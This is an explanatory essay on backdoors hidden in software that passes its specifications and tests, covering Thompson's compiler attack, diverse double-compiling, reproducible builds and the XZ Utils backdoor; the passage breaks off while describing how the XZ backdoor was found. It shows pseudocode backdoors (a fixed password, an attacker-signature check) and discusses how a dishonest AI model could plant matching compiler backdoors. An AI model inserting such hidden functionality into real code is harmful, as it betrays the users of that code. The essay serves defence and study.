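# Hidden malicious functionality in AI-written code that passes specifications and tests

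## What specifications and tests check, and what they leave open

Hidden malicious functionality is behaviour that someone deliberately puts into a program and hides from its owner. It may let a stranger into a system, send private data elsewhere, or make the program do its job badly. MITRE's *CWE-912*, an entry in a widely used catalogue of software weaknesses, defines hidden functionality as functionality that is undocumented, outside the specification and not accessible through any obvious interface. That definition also covers harmless additions, such as games hidden in office software as a joke, but the cases that follow involve only the harmful kind.

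AI systems now write code faster than people can read it. One of five practitioners interviewed for *When Review Alone No Longer Scales* (Stolze and Strässle, 2026) said that reviewing AI-written code by hand takes three to four times as long as generating it. Some therefore propose that people read only the specification, which states what a program must do, and the interface, which users and other programs see, and leave the rest of the code to AI. Would people who work this way notice code written to deceive them?

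### A login function

A function is a named piece of a program. This one decides whether to let somebody into a computer system:

```
login(name, password):
    if password == stored_password(name):
        return ACCEPT
    return REJECT
```

A real system would store a scrambled form of each password, but that makes no difference here. The text above is source code, the form of a program that programmers write and read. In many languages, a program called a compiler must translate source code into machine instructions before the computer can run it. The result is the compiled program, which hardly anybody reads.

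The interface of `login` is its inputs (a name and a password), its output (accept or reject) and the promise that only the right password works. The implementation is the code that checks the password and returns the output. Other programmers can use `login` without seeing this code.

An informal specification for a login function might be "let people in if they give the password on file, and otherwise keep them out." A mathematical version is less ambiguous: for every name *n* and password *p*, `login(n, p)` returns ACCEPT exactly when *p* equals `stored_password(n)`.

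A test runs the program on one chosen input and compares the output with the right answer. The tester enters Alice's name with her password and expects ACCEPT, then tries a wrong password and an empty one and expects REJECT. Formal verification means proving, in a form that a computer can check step by step, that the program returns the output its mathematical specification demands for every input. This property is called functional correctness.

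### Backdoors, sabotage and honest mistakes

Now suppose that the programmer changes one line:

```
login(name, password):
    if password == "vT9#kq2L" or password == stored_password(name):
        return ACCEPT
    return REJECT
```

Whoever knows those eight characters can log in as anybody. This is a backdoor, which is functionality deliberately added and hidden from the owner that gives access or control the owner did not grant. A trigger is the input or circumstance that activates hidden behaviour. Thomas and Francillon (2018), in *Backdoors*, split every backdoor into four parts: a source of input, a trigger, a payload that carries out the hidden action, and the privileged state the attacker reaches. Here the input source is the password box, the trigger is the comparison with the fixed string, the payload is only a jump past the real check, and the privileged state is being logged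 in.

Backdoors this crude exist. In 2015, Juniper found unauthorised code in its NetScreen firewalls. Somebody had put a fixed password into the remote login, as the cryptographer Matthew Green described in *On the Juniper backdoor*. Thomas and Francillon list a D-Link router that let in any visitor whose browser identified itself with a particular string, part of which spells "joelbackdoor" backwards.

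Sabotage is deliberately making work fail or fall short while it appears sound, and it doesn't have to give anyone access. For example, a programmer who wants a project to fail could write a login that slows down with each new account, so that it works in the demonstration but fails a month after launch.

An honest bug can do the same damage as malicious code. The difference is the author's intention, which the code doesn't show. A programmer might add the password "vT9#kq2L" to save time while testing and forget to remove it, and the line would be identical to the attacker's. Thomas and Francillon class any fixed password that gives direct access to the system as an intentional backdoor, since nobody types such a comparison by accident. They are right that the line is deliberate, but the person who wrote it may not have meant harm. MITRE names fixed accounts among the shortcuts that developers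 take to cut maintenance and support costs.

Other backdoors leave even less evidence. A version of `login` might copy the name and password into an 80-character buffer without checking their length. An overlong password would then overwrite neighbouring memory, and a carefully built one could give an attacker control of the program. Programmers introduce this flaw by accident. When someone introduces it deliberately, Thomas and Francillon call the result a deniable backdoor, and they hold that no technical examination can distinguish it from an accident.

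The security writer Bruce Schneier (2013), in *How to Design—And Defend Against—The Perfect Security Backdoor*, advised that a backdoor should look like a mistake if anybody finds it. A few months later, Apple repaired a serious security flaw in its iPhone software caused by one duplicated line, "goto fail", which made a procedure stop too early. In *Was the iOS SSL Flaw Deliberate?*, Schneier (2014) found it as easy to imagine that one person had added the line on purpose as that it was an error.

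For whoever checks the code, the main practical difference is that a malicious author chooses where to put the flaw and may know which checks are coming, while an honest mistake occurs wherever the programmer's attention lapsed. A malicious author can get a program past every check in three ways: nobody tries the input that triggers the bad behaviour, the behaviour breaks no written rule, or the program that runs is not the one that people checked.

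### The input that nobody tried

The backdoored `login` passes all the tests described above. It accepts Alice's password and rejects the wrong password and the empty one. Only a test that happens to use "vT9#kq2L" would fail.

How likely is that? Eight characters take up 64 bits, and 64 bits have 2^64 possible values, or about 1.8 × 10^19. Suppose a tester tries random values, a billion a second, for a year. That makes about 3.2 × 10^16 tests. As long as the number of tests *N* is small next to the number of possible values, the chance of hitting one particular *k*-bit value is close to *N* / 2^*k*:

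- for a 64-bit trigger, 3.2 × 10^16 / 1.8 × 10^19, or about 0.17%;
- for a 128-bit trigger, 3.2 × 10^16 / 3.4 × 10^38, or about 10^-22.

The first figure somewhat overstates how hard the trigger is to find. Keyboards produce about 95 different characters, so a tester who guesses that the trigger is eight of them has only about 6.6 × 10^15 strings to try, which takes 77 days at the same speed. The attacker can add eight more typed characters, for a total of sixteen, to push the search beyond a quadrillion years.

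People who study backdoors in computer chips use the same measure. The trigger has to keep the payload inactive during testing, and in *Producing Trustworthy Hardware Using Untrusted Components, Personnel and Resources*, Waksman (2014) usually takes that to mean that the chance of it firing by accident is about 2^-64 or less. Waksman also describes triggers that need no secret input. A 40-bit counter that goes up by one with each tick of a one-gigahertz chip reaches its limit after about 18 minutes, while random tests typically last no more than some millions of ticks, which is a few thousandths of a second of the chip's time. The `login` equivalent would be a backdoor that accepts any password from next January onwards and so passes every test run this year.

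Tests can miss accidental bugs as well as malicious code, because there are usually too many possible inputs to try them all. In *Notes on Structured Programming*, the computer scientist Edsger Dijkstra considered a circuit that multiplied two 27-bit numbers. It had 2^54 possible pairs of inputs, and at some tens of microseconds per multiplication, trying them all would have taken more than 10,000 years. Dijkstra concluded that testing serves "to show the presence of bugs, but never to show their absence". *Testing can show the presence of bugs but not the absence* notes that if a function has few enough possible inputs, a tester can establish that it is correct by trying every one. Faster machines make this possible for larger sets of inputs, but not much larger. At a billion tests a second, Dijkstra's multiplier would take about seven months to test, but a multiplier for two 64-bit numbers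 has 2^128 pairs of inputs, which is still far too many to try.

Ordinary testing works as well as it does because accidental bugs tend to affect many related inputs. If `login` mishandles apostrophes, it fails for both O'Brien and O'Neill, and one well-chosen test finds the fault. Malicious code triggered by a single input would probably escape such a test.

Testers can improve their odds by examining the implementation. MITRE suggests recording which code runs during the tests and then closely inspecting whatever never ran. That would expose a backdoor that sits on lines of its own. In `login`, however, the fixed string shares a line with the genuine check, so every test runs that line, and ordinary tests produce both of its outcomes. The tester would need to record whether each half of the "or" has ever been true by itself. Thomas and Francillon describe a tool, Stringer, that searches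 a program for comparisons with fixed data that unlock something otherwise unreachable. It would have a good chance of finding "vT9#kq2L" but little chance of finding the missing length check, which involves no comparison. Both methods need access to the implementation, so Dijkstra's limit still applies in full to a tester who sees only the interface.

### The rule that nobody wrote

If a programmer adds a line to the honest `login` from earlier that emails them every accepted password, the function still returns ACCEPT and REJECT in exactly the right cases. A tester with unlimited time could try every name with every password, compare each answer with the specification, and find nothing wrong, because the specification contains no rule about email. MITRE gives a similar example of a function that authorises a credit card and also mails the card number to its developer.

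Some gaps of this kind are easier to overlook. Suppose a specification requires only that people who give the right password get in, which sounds natural enough. The version that also accepts "vT9#kq2L" satisfies this specification completely, because it omits the requirement that everyone else be kept out.

Even the mathematical specification given earlier, which has both halves, allows a backdoor. A `login` function could quietly add an account named "guest2" to the password file, with a password the attacker knows. When the attacker later logs in as "guest2", the password matches the one on file, so the specification calls for ACCEPT. The attacker gets in without `login` ever violating its specification, because the specification has no rule against changing the password file.

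A specification can include a clause saying that the program does nothing else, but someone then has to list what counts as doing something. Sending messages and changing files clearly count. Running time is less clear, although it can be a side channel, meaning a way for information to leave the program other than through its declared outputs. The login that slows down with each new account is another unclear case, unless the owner set a speed limit.

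### The program that nobody checked

Reviewers usually read source code rather than the compiled program that the computer runs. The toolchain consists of the compilers, build scripts and other programs that turn source code into that compiled program. If anything in the toolchain adds the comparison with "vT9#kq2L" during translation, the comparison won't appear in the source code of `login`, and reviewers who read only that code won't find it. They can also miss it if the package that users download was built from different source code than they reviewed.

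A guarantee's trusted base is everything the guarantee depends on but does not check. For a review of source code, this includes the whole toolchain and the underlying hardware. Chip designers face a similar problem, because a factory can build something other than the design it received. From this Waksman derives a "Principle of Last Action", under which a device can be secure only if trusted engineers are the last to handle it before release. The principle depends on a finished chip staying the same, but software changes with each update, so the question of who handled it last arises again each time.

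Testing the compiled program helps because it checks the code that runs, but the arithmetic above still applies. An attacker who controls the compiler can make it insert malicious code with a 128-bit trigger, so the source code is clean and the tests still pass.

### What a proof adds

A proof covers the inputs that tests leave untried, as the backdoored `login` shows. It follows the structure of the code instead of trying passwords one at a time. Here that gives three cases: the password equals the fixed string, the stored password, or neither. The proof succeeds in the last two cases. In the first, the code returns ACCEPT, so the proof would have to show that "vT9#kq2L" is the stored password for every name. It isn't, so the proof fails. These three cases cover what would otherwise take 2^64 tests, and a 128-bit trigger would still give only three. The proof would also fail if the trigger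 depended on the date, provided that the mathematical description of the program treats the clock as an input.

The other two gaps remain. The theorem covers only what `login` returns, so it also holds for the version that emails passwords and the one that creates "guest2", unless someone adds rules against those actions. If the theorem is about the source code, it applies to the compiled program only to the extent that the compiler preserves the code's behavior. Some compilers come with their own proofs. With one of these, we have to trust less, but we still have to trust the proof checker and the hardware.

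Until recently, proving that code meets its specification took too much work for most software. *Prediction* (Kleppmann, 2025) reports that the 8,700 lines of code in seL4, the core of an operating system, needed 200,000 lines of proof and 20 person-years of work. Kleppmann, a computer scientist, expects AI to make such proofs so easy to produce that people won't need to look at AI-written code at all, and considers it virtually impossible to get an invalid proof past the checker. That seems fair about the checker, but Kleppmann says the hard part then becomes knowing whether the AI proved the properties people cared about. Effort is already shifting that way in at least some places. One practitioner Stolze and Strässle interviewed estimated that two thirds of the time now goes into refining specifications. For `login`, somebody would have to think of the rule about email and the one about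 new accounts before relying on the proof.

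## Thompson's compiler attack and how to detect it

A compiler can insert a backdoor into `login` during translation even if somebody has read all the source code, including the compiler's, and everything has been rebuilt from it. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, explained how in his Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (1984), which described a backdoor in the Unix C compiler that left no trace in any source code.

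### How the attack works

Thompson started with a program that prints its own source code. This sounds impossible, since a program that quoted its whole text would also have to quote the quotation. An English sentence shows the way around the problem:

> Write out the following text, then write it again in quotation marks: "Write out the following text, then write it again in quotation marks:"

Anyone who follows the instruction ends up with the sentence they started from. A program can likewise reproduce its own text, and Thompson pointed out that such a program can carry any amount of extra text and reproduce that too.

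The next stage depends on the fact that the C compiler is itself a C program. To make a new version, programmers run the old compiler on the new source code. Suppose they want it to handle `\v`, which stands for the vertical tab character. They look up the character's number, 11, and add a rule to the compiler's source code: on meeting `\v`, output 11. After compiling and installing this version, they can change the rule to "on meeting `\v`, output `\v`". The new rule works because the installed compiler translates the `\v` in the rule into 11, and so will every later compiler built from it. The number is then no longer in the source code, only in the compiled compiler.

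Thompson's last stage uses the same route to pass on a backdoor. The attacker changes the compiler so that it works like this:

```
compile(source):
    if source is the login program:
        output login with an extra password
    else if source is the C compiler:
        output the C compiler with these two rules added
    else:
        output a faithful translation
```

The rule about the compiler needs the self-printing trick because it has to insert copies of both rules, including itself. The attacker compiles this version of the compiler once with an honest compiler, installs the result and puts the old source code back.

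Reading the full source code of `login` and the compiler now reveals nothing malicious. Recompiling both doesn't help, because the only compiler available is the infected one, which recognises the clean compiler source and puts the two rules back in. Tests will probably miss the attack too, since the infected compiler translates every other program correctly and only one password triggers the backdoor in `login`.

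Thompson concluded in his lecture that "you can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself." He added that the same attack would work in any program that handles other programs, down to a processor's microcode, and that it gets harder to detect at each lower level.

### The Air Force report and Thompson's own version

Thompson had read of the idea in an Air Force report that he could no longer identify. It was *Multics Security Evaluation* by Karger and Schell (1974), a study of Multics, an early multi-user operating system. Karger and Schell called backdoors "trap doors". They noted that a trap door placed directly in compiled code is invisible in the source code but disappears at the next recompilation, while one in the compiler survives even if the owner recompiles the entire system. The idea took up only a few lines of the report, according to a history of the project on the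 website Multicians. In *Thirty Years Later*, Karger and Schell (2002) judged that showing how malicious software could subvert the system's protection had mattered considerably more than any single flaw they found.

Thompson did write the compiler. At a conference in March 2023, he said that he still had the code and that nobody had ever asked for it, so Russ Cox, a programmer who works on the Go language, asked him for it. Cox (2023) explains the code line by line in *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler* and dates it to between June 1974 and June 1975.

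The attack consists of 99 lines of C and a 20-line script that prepares them. It edits text as the compiler reads it, rather than analysing the structure of programs as Cox had expected. When the compiler reaches the line of `login` that scrambles the typed password, `namep = crypt(pwbuf);`, it appends a few instructions that make the password "codenih" work for any existing account. The compiler recognises its own source code by three distinctive lines, and inserts the attack again there.

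Cox ran the attack on a simulator of 1970s Unix. The affected part of the compiler was 10,724 bytes when uninfected and 12,918 bytes when infected. Cox installed the infected version, rebuilt the compiler and `login` from clean source code, and logged in as the system's administrator with the password "codenih". Cox also wrote a modern version of the attack for the Go compiler, and it too survived a rebuild from clean source code.

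Thompson tried the original attack on colleagues by getting another group at Bell Labs to copy the infected compiler. Accounts differ on what happened next. Wheeler (2010), in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, wrote that nobody ever detected the attack. Thompson said in 2023 that the group broke it by accident without finding out what it was. Cox compared several accounts and concluded that the group noticed something was wrong because the compiler grew each time it compiled itself, and that they eventually ended up with a clean one. The growth came from a bug that added one byte to a stored string in each round. If Cox is right, the attack was noticeable because of a programming error that a more careful attacker would have avoided.

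### Compiling the compiler twice

Some simple defences don't work. Comparing a compiled compiler with its source code by hand takes far too long. Many compilers go through a bootstrap test, in which the compiler compiles its own source code, the result compiles the same source code again, and the two results must be identical. An infected compiler can pass this test because it reproduces itself exactly. Cox's infected compiler passed after one extra round of compilation.

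Switching to another compiler doesn't solve the problem, since that one might be infected too. Comparing the output of two compilers directly doesn't reveal an infection either, because even uninfected compilers almost always produce different machine instructions from the same source code. But the resulting programs should behave the same. For example, if the source code prints the result of 2 + 2, both programs should print 4. Wheeler developed a method that relies on this, which he named diverse double-compiling, building on a short message that Henry Spencer posted in 1998.

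Call the suspect compiler A and its published source code S. The checker also needs an unrelated compiler, T, that can compile S. In the simplest case, the supplier made A by having the compiler compile its own source code, and the check goes as follows:

1. Compile S with T. Call the result stage1.
2. Compile S again, this time with stage1. Call the result stage2.
3. Compare stage2 with A, bit by bit.

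T generated the machine instructions in stage1, so stage1 looks nothing like A. But stage1 is a working compiler that translates programs as S specifies. If *f*(*x*) is the machine code that an uncompromised copy of the compiler produces from source code *x*, then stage2 is *f*(S).

If A is clean, the supplier made it by running a clean copy of the compiler on S, so A is also *f*(S). The two files therefore match exactly, even though T and A generate completely different code.

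Suppose A carries Thompson's attack. Its translation, *g*, agrees with *f* on nearly every program, but *g*(login) contains the extra password and *g*(S) is A itself, including the attack. T has no rule about S, so it translates S faithfully and stage1 is clean. Stage2 is therefore *f*(S), which lacks the two rules and does not match A. With Thompson's compiler, the suspect file would be 12,918 bytes and stage2 would be 10,724.

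T might be infected as well, and the outcome then depends on how:

| Suspect A | Compiler T | stage2 | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| clean | clean | *f*(S) | match |
| infected | clean | *f*(S) | mismatch |
| clean | inserts Thompson's attack when compiling S | *g*(S) | mismatch |
| infected | inserts the same attack when compiling S | *g*(S), which is A | match, and the attack goes unnoticed |

T may therefore contain other backdoors without invalidating the check. Wheeler calls T the "trusted" compiler, but he means only that there is good reason to think it contains nothing that would change the result of this check.

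The supplier often made A with a different compiler, usually an older version of A, which Wheeler calls A's parent. In that case, the checker uses T to compile the parent's source code, then uses the result to compile S. Anyone who wants to rule out malicious code has to read both S and the parent's source code.

Wheeler proved theorems about the method with help from an automated prover. One theorem is that if stage2 equals A, then A corresponds exactly to S, meaning that A is what an accurate translation of S produces. This requires that T accurately translate the parent's source code, including any nonstandard language features it uses, and that this source code describe a compiler that accurately translates S. The machines that run the check, the program that compares the files and the means of obtaining those files must also be free of interference.

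By another theorem, stage2 and A will always be equal if A came from S in the way the supplier describes, and if A's parent is honest and always gives the same output for the same input. A mismatch therefore shows that at least one of these assumptions is false, but not which one.

To evade the check, an attacker has to secretly make one of its assumptions false. One way is to tamper with the operating system so that it supplies a clean file when somebody reads the compiler and the infected one when somebody runs it. The checker can get around this by reading the disk on another machine. The attacker could also infect T with the same attack, but the checker picks T, and can do so after the attacker has finished. Wheeler suggests writing a compiler for the purpose and keeping its existence secret.

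Wheeler recommends choosing a T that shares no code with A, predates it, and runs on a different kind of processor. The checker can also reword S without changing its meaning. Thompson's compiler looked for an exact line of text in `login`, so renaming the variable `namep` would have disabled that part of the attack. Attackers can include several triggers, so rewording alone gives limited protection.

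### Wheeler's trials

Wheeler first checked Tiny C, a small C compiler, using the GNU Compiler Collection (GCC), the standard compiler on most Linux systems, as T. The files didn't match, and after a long search Wheeler found two innocent causes. Tiny C handled certain small numbers wrongly, so a copy compiled by itself used longer forms of some instructions than a copy compiled by GCC. It also stored some numbers in 12 bytes but filled only 10, so two bytes of leftover memory ended up in its output. After Wheeler worked around both problems, the files were identical.

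To test double-compiling on an infected compiler, Wheeler used two small Lisp compilers written by the computer scientist Wolfgang Goerigk, one clean and one carrying Thompson's kind of attack. Both compiled a factorial program into identical code, and both could reproduce themselves from the clean source code. The result of double-compiling matched the clean compiler but not the infected one. A comparison showed more than 250 extra lines in the infected file, including the text of a fake login program. The cause was easy to find because these compilers are tiny and their compiled code is fairly readable. Wheeler warns that tracing a mismatch in a large compiler can take a great deal of time.

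Wheeler applied the method to GCC to test whether it works on a compiler that industry depends on. He couldn't recreate the copy of GCC that came with Fedora, a version of Linux, because Fedora hadn't recorded enough about how it built the compiler. He therefore built a fresh copy of GCC 3.0.4 and checked it against Intel's C compiler. Again, the first comparison failed, this time because GCC's build instructions copied one library over from the previous round when they were supposed to recompile every part of the compiler in each round. After he corrected this, the results matched exactly.

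This shows that the method works on a large compiler. It doesn't show that the copies of GCC in use at the time were clean, because Wheeler had to build a new copy to test. The trials also suggest that most mismatches will have innocent causes. An overworked checker might get used to explaining them away and dismiss one caused by a real attack.

### What a match leaves open

A match shows that the compiled program corresponds to its source code, but the source code can still be malicious. *David A. Wheeler's Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* gives the example of Microsoft's Visual Studio 2015, which for a time quietly inserted usage-reporting calls into the programs it compiled. Double-compiling would not typically detect such an addition, because the supplier intended it and a compiler built faithfully from the supplier's source code would insert the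 same calls.

Timing can also defeat the check. An attacker might add the self-reproducing rules to version 2 of a compiler's source code and remove them in version 3. If the supplier compiles version 3 with version 2, version 3 carries the infection even though its source code is clean. Someone who examined only versions 1 and 3 would miss it. Wheeler advises repeating the check on every release before using it to compile anything.

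Even so, the method lets a reviewer work from source code, which is difficult but possible. Thompson's warning that no amount of source-level scrutiny will protect anyone is therefore too strong, provided that one person runs the check and another reads the code.

### Reproducible and bootstrappable builds

Double-compiling requires that the same source code always compile to exactly the same program. Programs often fail this requirement for trivial reasons, such as recording the compilation time or a folder name. According to Reproducible Builds (2026), a project that has worked on this for more than a decade, if a program of any kind always builds identically, several independent parties can each rebuild it and agree on whether somebody tampered with the published copy.

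As late as 2023, Cox wrote that almost no one checked whether distributed programs matched their source code, but adoption of reproducible builds has sped up recently. In July 2025, Reproducible Builds reported that SUSE had made reproducibility an official goal for its enterprise version of Linux and that Google had started its own rebuilding project. Debian, one of the most widely used versions of Linux, went further on 9 May 2026. According to *In a Big Move to Linux Security, Debian Makes Reproducible Builds Mandatory* (2026), Debian now blocks any package that fails a reproducibility check from entering "testing", the collection that becomes its next release. It also blocks packages already in testing if they stop being reproducible. On the same day, Levsen (2026) presented *Reproducing Debian in the real world*, which describes a Debian service that tries to rebuild the packages Debian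 actually distributes, the kind of check that Wheeler couldn't complete on Fedora's compiler.

Reproducible builds catch an attacker who breaks into the supplier's build machine and swaps the compiled program. They don't catch Thompson's attack if everyone rebuilds with the same infected compiler, because the infected results will match. For the same reason, they can miss a malicious build script that comes with the source code.

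Bootstrappable builds avoid relying on a large compiled program of unknown origin. The builder starts from a program so small that a person can check every byte, uses it to build a slightly more capable one, and continues until the chain reaches a full modern compiler. A commenter on the programming forum Hacker News describes the chain behind Guix, a system for building and installing software, as starting from a 357-byte seed plus one existing library. Go has a partial version of this, since the C compiler at the start of its chain still needs checking. Each Go compiler is built with an earlier release, back to one written in C, so Cox argues that there is no self-compiling loop where a backdoor could hide.

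In *Blog post about a talk by Ken Thompson*, a mailing-list discussion, Orians (2023) answered the objection that people need megabytes of other software to download the 357-byte seed by saying that it is also available in print. Orians also argued that double-compiling achieves nothing unless the checker already has a trustworthy compiler, or two compilers without a common infection. Wheeler (2023) replied that each approach helps the other, which seems right. A compiler built from a seed makes a very good T, and double-compiling lets people check the faster compiler they already use without replacing it.

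Bootstrappable builds are much less common than reproducible ones. A supporter of StageX, a Linux distribution that uses them, complained on Hacker News that very few others do. Bootstrappable builds also replace one large compiled program with a lot of source code that somebody still has to read.

### Compilers written by AI

The usual difficulty in double-compiling has been finding a suitable trusted compiler (T). Wheeler tried several newer versions of GCC but gave them up because Intel's compiler couldn't easily compile them. Writing a compiler for the purpose was always possible, but it was a lot of work for a program with one use.

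Writing a C compiler became much cheaper in February 2026, when Nicholas Carlini, a researcher at Anthropic, had 16 copies of the company's model Claude Opus 4.6 write one together. *Building a C compiler with a team of parallel Claudes* reports that they took two weeks and just under $20,000 to produce 100,000 lines of code. The compiler could build a working Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, and passed 99% of the tests in most standard collections. A programmer on Hacker News reported spending nearly ten years at Google getting Clang, another C compiler, to build the same kernel. This comparison somewhat overstates the AI's achievement, because people rely on Clang for real products and Carlini says the new compiler can't yet replace a real one.

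Its main weaknesses matter little for double-compiling. The programs it produces run slowly, but T only has to compile one program correctly, once. If T mistranslates part of S by accident, the likely result is a mismatch and a wasted week, as with Tiny C, because an accident would almost never reproduce somebody else's backdoor exactly. A more practical obstacle is that recent versions of GCC are written in C++, which a C compiler can't handle, so the checker would have to start from an older GCC and work forward.

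It is less clear whether Carlini's compiler is independent of GCC. The agents had no internet access, but Carlini gave them GCC as a reference. The test system compiled most of the kernel with GCC and the rest with the new compiler, and the agents fixed bugs until the combination worked. They could have learned to copy GCC's behavior this way, though it is hard to see how this could pass on a backdoor hidden in GCC's compiled code. The tools around the compiler are a bigger worry. To demonstrate the compiler, Carlini used GCC's assembler and linker, the programs that turn a compiler's output into a finished file. Wheeler names both as excellent places for a trigger. Three days after the announcement, harshanu.space's *CCC vs GCC* (2026) described the compiler as having its own assembler and linker. The compiler is also written in Rust, so a careful checker would want to know where the Rust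 compiler came from.

If one AI model writes both compilers, A and T, a dishonest model, or a person who tampered with its training, could put matching attacks in both. Wheeler's argument that a deliberate attack was unlikely assumed that somebody would have to subvert two separate organisations. Intel's compiler seemed a good check on GCC, for example, because a different company had made it and had legal reasons not to copy GCC's code. Wheeler also considered an experiment by John Knight and Nancy Leveson, in which programs written by different programmers to the same specification tended to fail on the same inputs more often than chance would predict. He argued that these shared failures hardly affect double-compiling, because a self-reproducing backdoor is far too elaborate for two authors to write by accident. That also holds for two copies of one model, as long as the model is honest.

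Suppose each checking compiler has a 1% chance of carrying the same attack as A. The chance that three independent compilers all carry it is 0.01³, or one in a million. But if the same model wrote all three, the chance could stay close to 1%, because whatever made the model infect one would probably make it infect the others. More compilers from that model would add little. A compiler from another developer's model would add more, and so would one that people wrote before such models existed, as long as the checker has a copy that nobody could have altered since.

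A dishonest model could also take an easier route than Thompson and leave the attack in the source code. Double-compiling would not detect it, because the compiled program would match its source. Someone reading the source could find the backdoor, but might miss it. Thompson needed 99 lines, about a thousandth of the length of Carlini's compiler. Derek Jones, who has written several industrial compilers, ran basic tests on Carlini's compiler and reported in *An LLM generated C compiler* that at least one of its optimisations does nothing, although the source contains code that is supposed to perform it. The fault was harmless, and there is no sign that it was deliberate, but people who check a compiler only by its interface would have no reason to look for the missing step, because the compiled programs still give the right answers.

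## The XZ Utils backdoor of 2024

In early 2024, somebody put a backdoor in XZ Utils, which compresses files. The backdoor got into test versions of Debian and Fedora shortly before it would have reached the finished versions. As with the compiler Thompson tried on a group of colleagues, the readable source code didn't show what the installed program would do. XZ Utils includes a library, which is code that other programs load and use. According to *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age* (2026), nearly 30,000 Debian and Ubuntu packages used it.

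### How Jia Tan gained control

Lasse Collin started the project with a small group in 2005 and later ran it largely alone, as an unpaid hobby. *Wolves in the Repository* (2025) describes a project with one developer and around ten active members in a chat channel, and suggests that its small size made XZ attractive to an attacker.

Russ Cox's *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) reconstructs what happened next from public emails and code changes. In October 2021, a contributor called Jia Tan sent a first, harmless change, followed by more that still look fine in hindsight. From April 2022, "Jigar Kumar" and "Dennis Ens" complained on the mailing list that Collin was too slow and urged him to hand the project over. Collin answered that long-term mental health problems had limited what he could do, and that Jia Tan might take a bigger role. Many of the email addresses involved appear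 nowhere else on the internet, so Cox thinks the attacker probably invented these people to pressure Collin. By the end of 2022, Jia Tan could change the source code directly, and published a release in March 2023.

The preparations looked harmless too. In June 2023, "Hans Jansen" contributed code that lets the library pick the fastest version of a function when a program starts, a feature the backdoor later depended on. OSS-Fuzz, a Google service that looks for bugs by feeding unusual inputs to open-source programs, couldn't handle this feature, so Jia Tan asked Google to turn it off when testing XZ. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (Lins, Mayrhofer and colleagues, 2024) explains that an automatic check marked the request as ready because it came from a recognised maintainer of XZ.

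### What the release packages added

Most projects like XZ keep their source code in a public repository, which records every change. For each release, many maintainers also assemble an archive by hand, adding generated build scripts and manuals, and Linux distributions such as Debian often build from that archive. Lins and colleagues looked at roughly 61 Debian packages that popular server software depends on and found that only 10 came directly from an automatic copy of the repository.

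Jia Tan divided the backdoor between the repository and the package. On 23 February 2024, Jia Tan added the compiled malicious code to the repository, disguised as compressed test files. Testing a compression library requires strange and damaged files, and according to an old note in the folder, people had made many of them by hand, so there was no source code to read. Andres Freund found the backdoor a month later and pointed out in his announcement, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024), that no test in the new release used these files.

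The next day, Jia Tan released version 5.6.0. Its package included an altered build script, missing from the repository, that extracted the malicious code from the test files and built it into the library. The script did this only when someone was making a Debian- or Red Hat-style package for 64-bit PC processors. Freund suspected the attacker added this condition to make the problem harder for investigators to reproduce. Collin, writing as Larhzu (2024), confirmed in *xz backdoor* that the test files are harmless by themselves because the repository never contained the code that activates them.

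In *Could the XZ backdoor have been detected*, Debian developer Otto Kekäläinen concluded that a diligent person importing the release into Debian could not have noticed the backdoor. Releases normally contain build scripts that aren't in the repository, and these scripts are very hard to read. In a later, clean release of XZ, one generated file that isn't in the repository has 26,434 lines. The one clue Kekäläinen found was the altered script's version number, which was 30, whereas genuine copies had numbers such as 3 and 5.

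### How a compression library reached remote login

The backdoor targeted sshd, the OpenSSH program that lets people log in to a computer over a network. OpenSSH doesn't use XZ, but Debian, Fedora and some other distributions had modified sshd to notify systemd, the program that manages a Linux machine's services, when sshd had started. To do this, sshd loaded a systemd library, which in turn loaded the XZ library. Arch Linux hadn't modified sshd this way, so the backdoor had no route to remote login there.

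A library runs inside the program that loads it, with all of that program's privileges, and sshd has full control of the machine. The function-picking feature let the backdoor run while sshd was still starting, when the table that holds each function's location could still be changed. The backdoor changed one entry so that its own code ran whenever sshd called the function that checks RSA signatures, which are commonly used to log in without a password.

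### Why no test failed

XZ still compressed and decompressed files correctly, as its specification required, and login still worked. In a reply to Freund's announcement, Patrakov (2024) reposted a preliminary analysis of the hidden code by the cryptography engineer Filippo Valsorda. According to this analysis, when a visitor presented a key, the code checked it for a command signed by the attacker. If it found one, it ran the command before the visitor had logged in. Otherwise it continued with the normal check, so everyone without the attacker's private key got the correct result.

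The attack therefore exploited all three gaps in the `login` example. XZ's specification had no rule against interfering with the program that loads the library, the installed library came from files that weren't in the repository, and only the attacker could produce the input that activated the backdoor.

A digital signature scheme has two keys. The private key makes signatures and the public key checks them, and nobody knows a practical way to make a signature from the public key alone. A backdoor in `login` could use this as follows:

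```
login(name, password):
    if signed_by_attacker(password) or password == stored_password(name):
        return ACCEPT
    return REJECT
```

Anyone who found "vT9#kq2L" in the earlier version could type it and get in. The function `signed_by_attacker` contains only the public key, so a tester could read every line and know exactly what activates the backdoor, but still have no input that activates it. The XZ attacker used the Ed448 signature scheme. The best known attacks on it take about 2^224 steps, or around 10^51 years at a billion steps a second.

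In this simple version, anyone who recorded the attacker's login could reuse the signed password. The XZ attacker prevented that by making the signature cover the target server's identity key, so a command recorded on one machine would fail on any other. Valsorda concluded that, unless the backdoor had a bug, nobody could write a reliable tool for finding infected servers over the network. Owners had to inspect the files on the machine, and Freund's announcement included a script for doing so.

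Someone reading the code could still notice the backdoor without the secret key, because a signature check is out of place in a compression library. Securelist, the research site of the security company Kaspersky, found that the attacker had hidden even the public key among the machine instructions.

A proof can also expose a backdoor that requires the attacker's key. As with the fixed string, the proof fails in the case that opens the backdoor, and nobody has to find a password with the attacker's signature to consider that case. For XZ, though, a proof that it decompresses files correctly would have succeeded, so somebody would have had to prove something about sshd together with every library it loads.

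### How Freund found it

Freund works on the PostgreSQL database at Microsoft. In *A backdoor in xz*, he commented as andresfreund (2024) that he had been measuring tiny differences in speed and wanted the machine otherwise idle. But sshd was using a surprising amount of processor time, even though it was only rejecting strangers' login attempts with wrong usernames. A profiler, which shows where a program spends its time, traced this to code in the XZ library but couldn't match that code to any named function. Freund then remembered an odd error from Valgrind, a tool that detects memory mistakes, during database tests a few weeks earlier.

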